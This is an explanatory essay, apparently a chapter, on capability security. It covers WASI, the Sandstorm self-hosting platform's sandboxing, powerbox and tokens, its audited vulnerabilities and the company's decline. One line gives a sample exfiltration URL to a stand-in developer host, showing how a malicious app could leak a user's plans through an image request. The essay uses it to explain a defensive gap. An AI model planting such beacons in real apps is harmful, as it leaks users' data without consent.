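The kernel's maintainers never merged the patches. Google worked on its own version of Linux with Capsicum for some years, but Ecosyste.ms' *Linux kernel with Capsicum support* lists it as archived and last changed in June 2020. One piece that did survive is an option to keep file access beneath a chosen directory. Maste (2018), in *namei*, traces a proposal for it to the Capsicum port, and Linux gained such an option in 2020 with the call `openat2`.

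### How a WASI program gets its files

WebAssembly is a format for compiled code that runs on many kinds of machine. A *module* can compute within its own memory but can affect anything else only by calling functions that its *host*, the program running it, supplies. WASI, the WebAssembly System Interface, standardises those functions for files, clocks, network connections and so on. According to WASI's *Security* page, a module starts with no access to the outside world and gets only the access the host explicitly grants.

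Suppose Ana wants to search her notes with a C program that she has compiled to WebAssembly. She runs it with Wasmtime, a widely used host:

`wasmtime run --dir=/home/ana/notes::/notes search.wasm`

1. Wasmtime opens the directory `/home/ana/notes` with Ana's rights, much as the shell opens files for `cat`.
2. It gives the module a descriptor for that directory, labelled `/notes`.
3. The program calls `open("/notes/today.txt")`, as it would on Unix.
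4. The C library inside the module matches the beginning of the path to the label, and asks Wasmtime for `today.txt` relative to that descriptor.
5. Wasmtime checks that the path stays inside the directory and opens the file.

If the program tries to open `/etc/passwd`, the library finds no matching directory and the call fails. As on Unix, the module can't gain access by making up a descriptor number. According to Wasmtime's documentation, the user can grant a directory this way at launch without changing file permissions.

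Ana's program needed no changes because the C library still accepts paths. This brings back part of the confused deputy problem. If she granted the program two directories, a stranger who supplied the path could choose which one it used. All the code in a module, including any library compiled into it, also shares the module's descriptors.

The host belongs to the trusted computing base. In 2026 developers made a one-line correction to Wasmtime to fix a bug that let a module erase the contents of files it was only supposed to read. The bug affected modules that had permission to change a directory but only to read the files in it. Miggo's *CVE-2026-47261* shows the faulty code, which did not count emptying a file as writing to it.

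### The state of WASI

The current version, WASI 0.3.0, came out on 11 June 2026. Its main addition is a standard way for *components*, which are modules with typed interfaces, to wait for slow operations and pass each other streams of data. In version 0.2, each component ran its own event loop, and the loops could not coordinate. Bytecode Alliance's *WASI 0.3* explains that the host now runs one loop for all of them. A component that receives a stream becomes its owner, and the sender can no longer use it.

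Many production systems still use WASI 0.1, which more hosts support. The standard version of Python has run on WASI since Python 3.11, but in March 2026 snarky.ca's *State of WASI support for CPython* still listed network sockets as unfinished because they depended on WASI 0.3 and thread support. WASI's developers are working towards a stable version 1.0 of the component system.

### Walls and what passes through them

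Containers, virtual machines and system-call filters all confine a program. A container gives the program its own view of the file system and running processes, a virtual machine gives it a simulated computer, and a filter blocks certain kinds of operation. Capabilities determine which outside resources the program can use, and even a well-confined program can do harm if it is given access to too many.

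For example, a shop runs a program to write its monthly sales report. The program runs in a container that has no security bugs, and the firewall lets it connect only to the shop's database. However, the administrator has given it the password for an account that can read and change every table. An attacker places an order with a product note that exploits a bug in the report program, and takes over the program.

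The container keeps the attacker away from the rest of the machine. But the attacker doesn't need the rest of the machine, since the customers' addresses and the orders are in the database. Now suppose the administrator had kept the password in a small service outside the container and given the program only a capability with one method, `monthlyTotals(month)`:

| Can the attacker ... | Container with the password | Same container with `monthlyTotals` |
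|---|---|---|
| read other files on the machine? | No | No |
| read customers' addresses? | Yes | No |
| delete every order? | Yes | No |
| put false figures in the report? | Yes | Yes |

Capsicum alone would not achieve this. MIT's notes explain that it treats a connection to a server as one capability, whatever requests the program sends over it, so the small service has to restrict those requests. The administrator could also create a database account that can read only the monthly totals, which would limit the damage just as well. But each different grant would need a new account, and anyone who learns an account's password can use it from wherever the database accepts connections.

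Filters also have to anticipate what a program will need. Bonzini described this problem in QEMU, which runs virtual machines. Users can attach devices to a virtual machine while it is running, so QEMU's filter had to allow every operation that any future device might require, which was generally too much. With capabilities, QEMU could receive access to each device when the user attaches it.

Capabilities still require isolation between programs. If the report program could read the memory of the service that holds the password, the narrow method would not protect the password. Capability mode provides this isolation, as does a WebAssembly module's separate memory. Sandstorm isolates applications using standard Linux features and passes capabilities across the boundary.

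### Why "access to photos" is coarse

Android runs each app under its own user ID, so by default one app cannot open another's files. But many of the permissions that apps request cover a whole category of data. If a user gives a messaging app access to photos in order to send one picture, the app and any advertising or analytics code inside it can read the entire library, including pictures taken later, until the user withdraws the permission.

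In *Sandbox Your Program Using FreeBSD's Capsicum*, Freeland (2025) calls such groupings "privilege silos", though his examples are `pledge` and the POSIX flags in Linux. A program that needs one privilege from a silo has to take all the others. Freeland admits that Casper's services can have the same fault. They therefore let a program give up the parts it does not need, for instance by restricting its network service to looking up one machine's address.

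A capability for the messaging app would refer to the one picture the user wants to send. The phone can provide it through a picker that runs outside the app. The picker can read the whole library, but the app receives only the picture the user taps. Android and iOS now offer pickers like this, and an app that uses one does not need the general photo permission. Capability designers call such a picker a *powerbox*.

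## How Sandstorm runs an untrusted app

Sandstorm is a platform for running web apps on a server owned by a person or a small organisation. Kenton Varda, who had worked on the data format Protocol Buffers at Google, announced it in March 2014 and began a crowdfunding campaign that July. A user installs an app from an app store with one click and uses it in a browser. Sandstorm's stated mission is for everyone to have a server on which they can install any software they want, though a friend or a hosting service may maintain the machine.

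Most people cannot tell a safe app from a dangerous one, and Sandstorm's developers did not expect them to learn. "Inevitably, such users will install malware," they wrote in the project's security overview. They wanted users to be able to run any app by any author without serious consequences. Their concerns included malicious apps, honest apps with bugs that let an attacker in, and commercial apps that secretly build advertising profiles of their users.

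Many of the first apps were existing open-source programs for ordinary Linux servers, such as the document editor Etherpad. Sandstorm therefore could not require a capability-safe language, and instead confines apps with Linux kernel features. In a comment on *Sandstorm personal cloud platform* (Edge, 2014), Varda said this choice let the team adapt existing apps quickly.

### A grain from start to finish

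Sandstorm's unit of isolation is the *grain*, one instance of an app with its own data. Every Etherpad document is a separate grain, with its own web server and its own database. Sandstorm's developer documentation describes the parts. Suppose Ana wants to write a packing list in Etherpad:

1. Ana installs the Etherpad package, an archive containing the app and every library it needs. The app's developer has signed it. Sandstorm accepts a later package as a new version only if it has a signature from the same key, and Ana has to confirm the upgrade.
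2. When Ana creates the document, Sandstorm starts a sandbox. The app can read the package but cannot change it. It can write only to the directory `/var`, which belongs to this grain alone.
3. A system-call filter blocks many of the kernel's less common functions. Sandstorm also leaves out the directories `/proc` and `/sys`, through which Linux programs normally learn about the machine.
4. The app gets no network connection. Its first process inherits one open socket, as file descriptor 3, and exchanges Cap'n Proto messages over it with a supervisor that serves only this grain.
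5. Ana's browser sends its requests to Sandstorm, which checks who she is and forwards them through the socket. A small program inside the grain, the HTTP bridge, turns them back into ordinary web requests for Etherpad.
6. When Ana closes the browser tab, Sandstorm stops the app. The packing list stays in `/var`, and Sandstorm starts the app again when she comes back.

The inherited socket does the same job as the two open files that the shell gives to `cat`. Etherpad starts with one connection, and it can reach something new only if a capability arrives over that connection.

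All grains on a server share one Linux kernel, so the kernel is part of the trusted computing base. Linux is far larger than seL4, and nobody has proved it correct. The filter reduces the risk by hiding parts of the kernel where bugs have been common. For example, apps cannot create user namespaces, which give a process its own set of user accounts and have caused many kernel vulnerabilities. In June 2014 the sandbox was unfinished, and Edge quoted the project's warning: "Malicious code probably can escape." The later security overview does not include this warning, but it describes no limit on the memory or processor time a grain may use.

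Sandstorm runs a separate server for every document, which would be wasteful if all of them ran at once. It runs only the grains that somebody has open, so an app has to start quickly. According to an explanation from Sandstorm's time as a company, apps often start in under a second, and some compiled apps use less than a megabyte of extra memory per grain because all grains of an app share the package's files. An app that needs to keep working after the tab closes has to request this, and Sandstorm then notifies the owner, who can refuse.

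### Who may open a document

On an ordinary server, one copy of Etherpad keeps everybody's documents in one database. The operating system cannot protect one document from readers of another, because the same program reads the same database for every user. Only Etherpad's own code can keep the documents separate, and a bug in that code may expose all of them.

Each grain holds one document, so permission to open the document is permission to reach the grain. Sandstorm can check that permission before the request reaches Etherpad. A new grain is private, and its owner shares it through Sandstorm's own interface.

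| | One Etherpad server for everyone | One grain per document |
|---|---|---|
| Who decides whether Ben may open Ana's list? | Etherpad | Sandstorm |
| What can an attacker read after taking over the app? | Every document | One document |
| Who stops Ben from editing if he may only read? | Etherpad | Etherpad |

The protection depends on how an app's packager divides its data. Sandstorm's guide for packagers recommends that a grain hold the smallest thing a user might want to share separately, such as one spreadsheet or one photo album. If a packager puts all of a user's albums into one grain, Sandstorm cannot share one album and withhold the rest.

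Sandstorm also handles logging in. It adds the user's identifier, display name and permissions on this grain to each request. Apps don't need passwords, so an attacker who steals an app's database finds none there. Ana can also create a sharing link, which is a capability in the form of a web address. Like E's Swiss numbers, the link works for anyone who learns it, even someone without an account.

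The last row of the table is one of the limits that the developers acknowledge. Sandstorm itself can only admit Ben or keep him out. If Ana lets him read the list but not change it, Sandstorm passes that restriction to Etherpad, which has to reject his edits. A bug in Etherpad could let his edits through. The limit still applies because each app defines and enforces its own permissions.

A stricter capability system would give Ben a read-only wrapper around the document. Sandstorm does not, for two reasons given in the comments to its interface definitions (Sandstorm, 2014). A wrapper outside the app would have access only to web requests, and with many older apps it could not easily identify the requests that change something. Each time somebody passed the document on, they would also add another wrapper, which might slow access to it.

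Having several capabilities to one document would also confuse people. Suppose Ana gives Carol permission to read the list, and Ben, who can now edit it, gives her permission to edit. Carol should see one document in her collection and be able to edit it. If Ben later withdraws his grant, she should still be able to read it. Sandstorm can do this because it computes Carol's permissions from both grants when she opens the document. With two separate wrappers, she would have to know which one to use.

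### A new web address for every visit

Each time somebody opens a grain, Sandstorm serves it from a new, random hostname that expires soon after the grain is closed. Browsers isolate pages from different hostnames, so a script in one grain cannot read another grain's page.

The random hostname also makes forged requests harder. In the stockbroker example, the malicious page needs the broker's address to send it an order. To forge a request to Ana's packing list, an attacker would have to guess an address that exists only for her current visit. The hostname serves much the same purpose as the secret that other sites put in their forms, and it protects apps whose developers forgot to add one.

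However, computers normally look up hostnames without encryption, so anyone who can watch Ana's network traffic can learn the address. Sandstorm's developers therefore advise that apps keep their own defences too.

### Connecting a grain to a calendar

A grain that can reach nothing is safe, but users often want apps to work together. Sandstorm's powerbox lets users connect them. Sandstorm's guide to the powerbox uses a calendar as its main example.

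Suppose Ana keeps her holiday plans in a grain of a trip-planning app and has shared the grain with Ben as an editor. Ben wants the travel dates in his own calendar. The trip-planning app has no information about which calendar app he uses or where to find his calendar.

1. Ben clicks a button in the trip planner. The app's page sends a request to the Sandstorm page that surrounds it:

```js
window.parent.postMessage({
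  powerboxRequest: {
    rpcId: 1,
    query: [calendarType],
    saveLabel: { defaultText: "Calendar for travel dates" }
  }
}, "*");
```

2. Sandstorm shows Ben a picker with all of his grains that offer this type of calendar. The trip planner cannot see the list.
3. Ben picks his family calendar. Its developer has defined two levels of access, reading only and full access, so Ben also chooses full access.
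4. Sandstorm sends the trip planner's page a *claim token*, which is valid only for Ben's current session. The page passes it to the part of the app that runs on the server.
5. The app exchanges the claim token for a lasting *access token*. It also states which permissions Ben must keep on Ana's grain for the connection to stay valid:

```
POST http://http-bridge/session/<Ben's session>/claim
{ "requestToken": "<claim token>",
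  "requiredPermissions": ["edit"] }
```

6. The app saves the access token in `/var` and includes it whenever it sends dates to the calendar.
7. A month later, Ana changes Ben from an editor to a reader. Ben has lost the "edit" permission, so Sandstorm revokes the connection and the app can no longer use his calendar.

The variable `calendarType` describes an interface, such as one compatible with Google Calendar. Any app that offers a compatible interface can fulfil the request. Ben could also pick an empty calendar if he didn't trust the trip planner with his real one.

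Ana may not know that Ben connected anything, so Sandstorm cannot rely on her to disconnect it. The interface definitions give the example of a forum moderator, Dave, who arranges to receive an email whenever somebody reports a post. If the forum's owner demotes him, the emails should stop, even though the owner never knew about them. This works only if the app names the right permission. If it names none, the connection lasts until Dave loses all access to the forum. Sandstorm also lists each grain's connections, so the owner can read the label from the first step and revoke a connection by hand.

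The exchange of tokens prevents a confused deputy attack. Suppose Sandstorm sent the lasting token straight to the browser. An attacker who shares the trip planner with Ana might steal the token for her calendar, start a powerbox request, and fake Sandstorm's reply with the stolen token in it. The app would respond as if the attacker had just chosen that calendar, and might show the attacker Ana's appointments. With the exchange, the app sends whatever it receives to Sandstorm as a claim token, and Sandstorm rejects a lasting token sent this way.

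### One step or two

With an access control list, Ben would have to tell the trip planner where to find his calendar, then open the calendar's settings and add the trip planner to the list of programs that may use it. With the powerbox, he only picks the calendar. The security overview points out that he would have to pick a calendar even if there were no security, since the app has to know which one to use.

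This is the same as the difference between `cp` and `cat`. Because Ben's choice also grants the access, Sandstorm doesn't need a separate prompt to let the trip planner use his calendar. People soon learn to answer such prompts without reading them. The comparison is slightly too favorable to Sandstorm, because Ben still has to choose between read and full access when the calendar offers both.

The powerbox can also grant narrower access than a user would think to grant. A forum that sends notifications normally needs a password for a mail server, and an attacker who takes over the forum can use that password to send spam. In the company-era design, the forum instead requests an "email recipient" from each user. The user picks an address, and the forum receives a capability to send mail only to that address.

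Access control lists have the advantage that an owner can see who has access, and Sandstorm's designers wanted to offer the same. Every capability passed between grains goes through Sandstorm, so the platform can list everyone who holds a capability to a given document. The owner can then revoke access for individuals on the list.

### What the token is worth to another grain

The access token is a string of random data. If a malicious trip planner passes the string to a second grain by the same developer, the second grain can't use it on Sandstorm. In E, as with a sharing link, having the string would be enough to gain access.

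Sandstorm (2014) gives the reason in its internal interface definitions. Sandstorm records an owner for every saved token. When a grain tries to use a token, its supervisor sends Sandstorm a request to *restore* it, which means turning the string back into a working capability. The request travels over a connection that Sandstorm set up for that grain, so the grain cannot impersonate another. If the grain does not own the token, the request fails. In this respect the token resembles the entry numbers in Dennis and Van Horn's C-lists, which meant nothing outside the program they belonged to.

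The trip planner can still misuse the calendar. If it has any way to communicate with the second grain, it can read Ben's appointments and pass them on, or carry out the second grain's requests. But the second grain has access only while the trip planner keeps doing this, and both lose access when Ben or Ana revokes the connection.

Sandstorm also issues tokens that work for anyone who has them. A user can create one to connect a phone app to a grain, for example. Sandstorm's *HTTP APIs* explains that the server uses the token to determine which grain to open, as which user and with which permissions. *forSharingAccidentally* (Weisz, 2025) showed that developers had misjudged how much access these tokens give, since each one also opens the grain's ordinary user interface.

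A grain cannot redeem such a token until the user pastes it into the powerbox. Otherwise, a malicious developer could hide a token in the app for a grain they control, and every copy of the app could send its user's data there. The internal definitions mention a temporary exception to this rule from before the powerbox existed.

### Earlier powerboxes: CapDesk and Polaris

Web browsers have long had a kind of powerbox. A web page cannot read files from the visitor's disk, but it can ask the browser to show a file picker and then receive the file the visitor chooses. CapDesk, the desktop Marc Stiegler built in E, used the same idea for all its programs. A program started with the few files it needed to run and received others when the user picked them.

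CapDesk required programs to be written for it. Stiegler, Karp, Miller and others then built Polaris at Hewlett-Packard's laboratories to protect existing programs on Windows XP. Polaris started a program such as Excel in a separate Windows account with very few rights. When the program tried to show its "open file" window, Polaris substituted its own. It copied the file the user chose into a folder that the restricted account could reach, and synchronized the copy with the original. A virus in a spreadsheet could damage that spreadsheet, but not the user's other files.

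The test version of Polaris did not restrict network access, so a virus could still send the open spreadsheet to somebody else. Polaris also had trouble with spreadsheets that refer to other spreadsheets, because the user had picked only the first file and the program had no access to the rest. Compilers have the same problem with source files that name other source files. A powerbox works best when the thing a user picks is complete in itself, as a Sandstorm grain usually is.

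### Do users expect access to follow their clicks?

CapDesk and Polaris applied the idea only to files. *User-Driven Access Control* (Roesner, Kohno and colleagues, 2012) extended it to cameras, location, text messages and data held by other apps. In this design, an app leaves space on the screen for a button that the operating system draws. When the user clicks the camera button, the system takes one picture and gives it to the app. The app never controls the camera, so it cannot take its picture later.

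They examined 100 popular Android apps to find out how often this would be enough. Across these apps they counted 143 separate uses of such resources:

| When the app needs access | Number | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Directly after the user does something | 89 | 62% |
| At set times or places | 11 | 8% |
| At any time | 12 | 8% |
| For something other than its main purpose, such as advertising | 11 | 8% |
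| Unknown | 20 | 14% |

Android at the time asked for permission when the user installed an app, and the app could then use the resource at any time. Roesner and colleagues concluded that only five of the 100 apps needed such permanent access to function. This figure depends on their judgement of what each app was for, and they could not find a purpose for one in seven accesses.

They also surveyed 186 users. Most thought that an app could not use a resource until the user pressed the relevant button, and more thought that it should not be able to. People worried less about their location than about the camera or text messages. In an earlier survey of 139 users, over 40% wrongly believed that an app could read the clipboard only when they pasted something. A powerbox restricts apps in the ways that many of these users expected.

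The surveys are stronger evidence for the idea than for any particular picker. Participants answered questions about screenshots, with nothing of their own to protect. Of the 186 participants, 154 were men and 92% had used a smartphone, at a time when many people had not. Sandstorm was meant for less technical users, and the study does not show how well they would choose.

One experiment did test behaviour. A window system for EROS had let apps draw their own "copy" and "paste" buttons, and relied on trustworthy text beside the mouse pointer to tell users what a button really did. Roesner and colleagues simulated attacks on this design by giving 139 participants buttons with false labels. 61% of participants did not notice the text beside the pointer, and the attacks succeeded in 87% of trials. In their own design, the system therefore draws the whole button. It also ignores clicks until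 the button has been fully visible in one place for 200 milliseconds, so that an app cannot slide it under the pointer just before a click.

Sandstorm likewise draws its picker outside the app's part of the page. An app could draw a convincing imitation, but picking a calendar there would not produce a claim token. No picker can prevent an app from giving a false reason for its request. Roesner and colleagues imagine a game of noughts and crosses in which every square is a button that reveals the player's location.

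*AUDACIOUS* (Ringer, Grossman and Roesner, 2016) later adapted the approach to unmodified operating systems. *User Interactions and Permission Use on Android* also suggests that separate permission dialogs may be unnecessary for resources that apps use mainly in response to the user, but recommends asking separately about background use. Sandstorm's powerbox does not make this distinction. Ben's one click gives the trip planner a token that never expires, so the app can read his calendar whenever it runs, even if he only wanted to add three dates.

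### Ways out that remained open

Sandstorm's overview says that an app cannot "phone home" to its developer unless the user allows it. The same document still lists exceptions, most of them dated April 2021. Fixes were planned, but Varda (2024) wrote that regular code contributions had stopped after late 2022, that he had stopped making monthly releases in early 2023, and that a group of volunteers had since taken over.

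Email was one exception. Sandstorm's developers had given apps an interface for reaching the network, which they named HackSessionContext to show that it was temporary. An early version of the packagers' guide mentions both web and email access. By April 2021 the security overview listed only limited sending and receiving of email, which the developers kept so that mail apps would work. They intended to remove this exception once users could grant email access through the powerbox.

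The browser was a more serious gap. A grain's server has no network connection, but its page runs in Ana's browser, which does. A malicious trip planner could make the page load an image from its developer's server, and write Ana's plans into the address of the image:

`https://developer.example/dot.png?plans=Lisbon-3-May`

Browsers can block such requests if the site sends them a Content Security Policy, a list of the servers that a page may contact. As of April 2021, Sandstorm had implemented this only partly, as an option for administrators, because it would have broken some existing apps. Sandstorm's policy still allowed images and media from any server. Content Security Policy also could not block WebRTC, a browser feature for video calls and other direct connections, and Sandstorm's developers were working with the standards process to change that. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level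 3* (2026) was still a working draft in August 2026.

A malicious app could therefore send its developer anything in its own grain while somebody had the grain open. It could not reach Ana's other grains unless she connected them to it.

In the overview, the developers also acknowledge covert channels, which no update is likely to remove. Two grains on the same server can signal to each other by varying how much processor time they use, much as in Lampson's examples. The developers note that such channels are usually slow, and hope that the risk of scandal or a lawsuit will keep companies from using them. That may deter a large company, but an anonymous malware author has little reputation to lose. Such an author would hardly need a covert channel as long as images can still carry data out through the browser.

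## Sandstorm's security record and why it stayed small

In February 2016, Sandstorm developers Asheesh Laroia and Kenton Varda checked its design against bugs that other people had found in ordinary copies of the apps. Laroia (2016) reported in *Sandstorm's security track record, and what it means for self-hosting* that Sandstorm had "wholly or partly mitigated" 95% of these bugs before they were disclosed.

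### What the 95% covers

Laroia and Varda looked at five apps: Etherpad, the website builder WordPress, the email program Roundcube, the scientific document editor ShareLaTeX and the news reader Tiny Tiny RSS. WordPress has so many published flaws that they included only those from 2014 and 2015 with a severity score of 6 or higher. They separately counted 21 Linux kernel flaws that the sandbox had blocked.

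The full list is in Sandstorm's documentation. It contains 20 flaws in the apps, 19 of them mitigated, which gives the 95%. Laroia and Varda did not mark which of the 19 they considered only partly mitigated, but they explained what protected users in each case:

| What protected users | Flaws | What an attacker could still do |
|---|---|---|
| Each document, mailbox or feed had its own grain | 8 | Attack a grain they could already open |
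| The grain had a random hostname | 5 | Succeed after learning the hostname |
| Sandstorm handled logins instead of the app | 3 | Nothing |
| Only editors could reach WordPress | 2 | Attack the site if they were editors |
| WordPress on Sandstorm had no comments | 1 | Nothing |

The five flaws in the second row are the clearest cases of partial protection, because Sandstorm cannot always keep the hostname secret. In the last row, users were safe only because WordPress on Sandstorm lacked a feature that it has elsewhere.

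### Two app flaws and Dirty COW

One of the Etherpad flaws was in its document export function. Because of a malformed database query, Etherpad returned every document whose identifier contained the requested text, so an outsider could collect all the documents on a server. Etherpad has the same bug on Sandstorm, but each grain holds only one document and only people with access to that document can reach the bug, so exploiting it reveals nothing they couldn't already read.

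A WordPress flaw from 2014 was more dangerous, since it let an attacker without an account run code on the server. Grains alone would not have protected the website, because a public site has to accept visits from strangers. The packagers' design protected it: WordPress produces the site's pages as static files, and Sandstorm itself sends them to visitors. Visitors cannot make any WordPress code run, so only people with access to the editing interface could exploit the flaw.

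This arrangement is also why the site has no comments. Laroia and Varda thought a separate app in its own grain could handle them. A bug there would at worst let an attacker deface other people's comments.

The one app flaw that Sandstorm did not stop was in Roundcube. An attacker could send an email containing a script, which ran when the victim opened the message. Sandstorm's access check did not help, because anyone can send mail to a mailbox without having access to it. The script controlled the mailbox page until the victim closed it, which was probably long enough to copy all the recent mail. It could not change who had access to the mailbox, because Sandstorm keeps those controls outside the app, and it could not regain control later, because Sandstorm gives the grain a new hostname at the next visit.

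Dirty COW was a flaw in the Linux kernel that could let any program take full control of the machine. Attackers were already using it when developers fixed it in October 2016. "COW" stands for copy-on-write, which means that programs can share one copy of a file in memory, and the kernel makes a private copy for any program that changes something. Because of a timing error, a program could sometimes change the shared copy, even if it was only allowed to read the file.

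A program could reach the faulty code in only a few ways, most of them meant for debuggers. Varda (2016) explained that Sandstorm apps could use none of them. The system-call filter already blocked `ptrace`, the call that debuggers use, and the sandbox left out `/proc`, which gives another way to access a program's memory.

Sandstorm stopped Dirty COW with a filter that any container platform could use, and capabilities played no part. If the filter had failed, the division into grains would have limited the damage. Varda thought a malicious app could then have read and changed other people's documents, but only documents that used the same version of the same app on that server.

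### How far to trust the figure

Laroia and Varda worked for the company that sold Sandstorm, and they decided what counted as mitigation. For each flaw, they explained why an attack would fail but did not report trying the attack. They called their list "not even remotely complete". It includes only apps that somebody had adapted to Sandstorm and that were popular enough for outsiders to look for bugs in them.

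Even a random sample of 20 flaws would give only a rough estimate. With 19 successes out of 20, the usual 95% confidence interval for the true rate runs from about 75% to almost 100%. This sample wasn't random, and nine of its flaws came from WordPress.

The choice of apps probably helped Sandstorm's security record. Etherpad and ShareLaTeX divide naturally into separate documents. A chat app such as Rocket.Chat, which Sandstorm also offered, has to put many people in one grain, where a flaw could let one member attack the others.

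The result is still worth taking seriously because outside researchers found these bugs without Sandstorm in mind, and readers can check each explanation against how the platform works. The protections don't depend on recognising a particular attack, so they should also apply to undiscovered bugs.

A year later, Taiwan's Department of Cyber Security commissioned an independent review from the security company DevCore. According to DevCore's *Sandstorm Security Review*, the testers found several flaws in the apps on a site that used Sandstorm, but could not use them to threaten the server. They then read Sandstorm's source code and found four flaws in the platform itself.

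### Mistakes in Sandstorm's code

Two of DevCore's four findings were ordinary programming mistakes. One was in the login system, which could treat everyone with an email address at a certain domain as a member of an organisation. Sandstorm's developers did not know that their email library could read one piece of text as several addresses. Sandstorm checked the domain of only one address, but the library sent the login message to all of them, so an outsider could log in as a member.

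Sandstorm failed to keep strangers from getting in as members, but it still isolated grains from one another. Varda (2017) explained that the intruder could install apps, create grains and find out who the other members were, but could not open anyone else's grains. Sandstorm fixed the mistake by checking addresses itself.

The other mistake affected backups. The tool that packs a grain's files into a backup runs in its own sandbox, which hid sensitive directories on the server. Sandstorm's developers later added two directories under new names and forgot to hide them. A check on file names also missed one case. Together, these errors let a user obtain a backup that contained some of the server's configuration files. Varda rated the flaw low severity because normally only the administrator can read the files with real secrets. The developers replaced the list of hidden directories with a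 list of permitted ones, so a new directory is now inaccessible unless someone adds it to the list.

DevCore praised Sandstorm's basic assumption that every installed app is malicious. It blamed most of the flaws on misused libraries and on new features whose developers had overlooked the existing defences.

### Gaps in the design

DevCore's other two findings were more than small coding mistakes. One was a confused deputy. Users could tell Sandstorm to download an app from any web address, and Sandstorm made the request from its own server, so a user could probe private services that only the server could reach. As with the billing file, the deputy used its own authority to act on a name the user supplied.

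Sandstorm's developers responded with a list of forbidden addresses, which includes private networks by default. Varda admitted that this would probably break some servers with their own private collections of apps, and that their administrators would have to edit the list. Sandstorm restricted apps with capabilities, but its own code still used ambient authority on behalf of users.

The last finding was that Sandstorm hardly limited the resources an app could use. It capped the number of files a process could open, but not the number of processes or the amount of disk space, so a malicious app could exhaust either and crash the server for everyone. The boundary between grains protected their data but not their share of the machine's resources. seL4's designers had dealt with part of this problem by requiring a capability for memory. Varda did not mention a fix for this finding in a post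 about the release that fixed the other three.

The same release closed a hole that David Renshaw, one of Sandstorm's developers, had noticed. Linux had a new flaw in its code for DCCP, a little-used network protocol that Sandstorm's system-call filter had not blocked. The published attack only crashed the machine, but Varda thought an expert might be able to use the flaw to break out of the sandbox. No change to Sandstorm could have prevented the bug itself. But Sandstorm runs every grain on one shared kernel, and the filter works only if its authors have guessed which parts of that kernel are dangerous, as they had for Dirty COW but not for DCCP.

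In May 2025 the volunteers who had taken over Sandstorm disclosed the problem with API tokens. These tokens connect outside programs to a grain, but they also open its ordinary interface. An app's developer can restrict a token to a *role*, a set of permissions that the app defines. Otherwise the token carries all the permissions of the user who created it. The documentation described an optional setting for tokens meant for sharing, which led developers to assume that tokens without it could not open the interface.

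Weisz explained that this did little harm in most apps, because their users kept the tokens private and expected them to give full access. It mattered for apps whose tokens are public. Hummingbird, which counts a website's visitors, must include its token in the site's pages, where any visitor can read it. With that token, a stranger could open the grain and watch the current visitors, including their approximate locations. The volunteers' own tool for collecting installation errors had the same fault, but held no data that identified anyone.

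Here the failure was in attenuation. Sandstorm could make a token that could only report visits, and Hummingbird's developer had defined a suitable role, but the token did not use it. Sandstorm enforced exactly the access the token carried, so the model worked as specified. The fault was in the interface, which made full access the default. The volunteers fixed two of the three affected apps and prepared a fix for Hummingbird, whose author they had not yet reached. They now refuse new apps that create such tokens without naming a role.

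### Why apps were hard to bring over

Few people used Sandstorm. Varda (2017) wrote that there were thousands of self-hosted servers, but according to a later post on Sandstorm's blog, only about 500 had ever used Sandcats, Sandstorm's free service for domain names and certificates. Oasis, the company's hosting service, had 2,642 monthly active users in August 2018, of whom 88 paid.

In October 2025, Varda (kentonv) and Jacob Weisz (ocdtrekkie), who leads the volunteers, discussed online why Sandstorm stayed small. Another user, goku12, blamed the way Sandstorm separates data. Most web apps keep all users' data in one database, manage their own accounts and contact other servers without restriction. Packaging an app for Sandstorm requires changing all three.

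Daniel Krol ran into this in 2023 while building a map app for Sandstorm. The usual software for serving maps depends on Postgres, which is designed for many users and is hard to run in a grain. Krol chose a map format that needs no database and used the much smaller SQLite for searches. This worked, but it meant designing the app around Sandstorm instead of packaging an existing one.

Running a separate server for each document also took a lot of time and memory, since not all apps were as quick and small as the company had advertised. In August 2026 Varda said the approach had not worked well because a server might take seconds to start and use hundreds of megabytes. If an app needed 200 megabytes, ten people with ten different documents open would need about two gigabytes, whereas an ordinary server could handle all of them with one copy of the app. Cloudflare OS reduces the startup time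 and memory use by running apps in isolates instead of containers.

Sandstorm's apps also had trouble working together. A grain can reach the outside world through the powerbox, but only if the app's developer has written powerbox requests into the app, and many developers never did. Some apps therefore lacked features on Sandstorm that they had elsewhere. Years after the company failed, a volunteer, Ian Denhardt, wrote a tool that intercepts an app's ordinary web requests and turns them into powerbox requests. Weisz thinks Sandstorm should have included something like it from the start.

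### The company runs out of money

Sandstorm raised about $60,000 through crowdfunding in 2014. Its first investors then put in $1.3 million, according to LWN's news item *Varda*. The company grew to seven people and planned to earn money from Sandstorm for Work, a paid version that let organisations connect their existing login systems and set their own access policies.

In his 2024 account of the company's history, Varda wrote that it had tried to raise more money in 2016 on the strength of developers' enthusiasm, as other start-ups had done, but investors weren't interested. The company then tried to find business customers quickly, but nobody on the team knew how to sell to large organisations, and it made only two sales. Companies that considered acquiring Sandstorm mainly wanted its engineers. The best offers were to take over the company for nothing and hire some or all of its staff.

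In February 2017 Varda announced that Sandstorm had run out of money. He blamed the team's inexperience in sales and the state of the product, which he still considered alpha quality. Hundreds of organisations had tried Sandstorm for Work, but almost none had bought it. This suggests the product was at least as much of a problem as sales, because these organisations had already found it. Varda later wrote that he would never know why the investors stayed away.

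The company made all the paid features free. A month later, most of the team joined Cloudflare, which runs a worldwide network for delivering websites (Varda, 2017, *The Sandstorm Team is joining Cloudflare*). Varda's project there became Cloudflare Workers, the platform on which he later built Cloudflare OS.

The team hoped that volunteers would continue developing Sandstorm. But Denhardt (2020) recalled in *Reviving Sandstorm* that outsiders had mostly built apps, and that only employees had regularly done major work on the platform. Varda continued to run Oasis in his spare time. In 2018 it cost about $700 a month more than it earned, and he paid the difference until he ended the free plan.

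By September 2019 Oasis had almost 200 paying users and made a small profit, but Varda decided to close it. Almost all its app packages dated from 2015 or 2016 and loaded very slowly, and he no longer felt right charging for them. He also worried that some customers were paying by mistake.

### What Varda would change

In 2019, Varda wrote that the company should never have created Oasis and should have concentrated on people who ran their own servers. In the 2025 discussion, he said he would no longer focus on existing apps. The best apps on Sandstorm were the ones written for it, and many had taken only an afternoon to write because the platform already handled logins and sharing. He also said that AI could now write most such apps, and that the sandbox would protect users from security bugs in the code.

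Weisz disagrees about existing apps. He thinks Sandstorm's biggest problem was a lack of well-known ones, and that making them easier to adapt would have helped. Both explanations fit what happened. People expected familiar apps, but the ones Sandstorm had were often old, slow or incomplete. Weisz has also found AI tools good at adapting apps to Sandstorm, so the work that held it back may now take much less effort.

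### The volunteers' project in 2026

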